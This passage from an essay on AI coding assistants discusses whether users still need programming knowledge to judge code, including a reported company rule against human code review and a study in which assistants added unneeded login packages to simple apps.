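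Others think that the baseline is moving from writing code to specifying and judging it. The San Diego teachers who introduced Copilot in the first week took this view when they gave more weight to reading and testing code. He and colleagues likewise expect human attention and judgement to become the bottleneck, and advise firms to decide in advance which changes can skip human review. The late-fee example fits this view, because the accountant's knowledge matters more there than the ability to write Python. This view differs from the first on whether people can learn to judge code without writing a good deal of it, and the experiments on learning give reasons to doubt that they can.

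The remaining position is that low-stakes work needs no baseline knowledge. If a record catalogue loses an entry, its owner can type it in again, which takes far less time than a programming course. According to *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices*, the software company StrongDM instructs its agents that code "must not be reviewed by humans", and it does not limit this rule to harmless projects. The rule excludes only human review, so a firm could follow it and still employ experts to write the requirements and design the tests.

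Ordinary users may find it hard to know whether the stakes are still low once the assistant has finished. Andročec identified 38 applications whose descriptions mentioned no users or accounts. Even with the plain prompt, 17 of them included a package for logins or sessions, and 36 did with the security paragraph. Someone who asks for a harmless tool may therefore get one that collects passwords, and people often reuse their email password.
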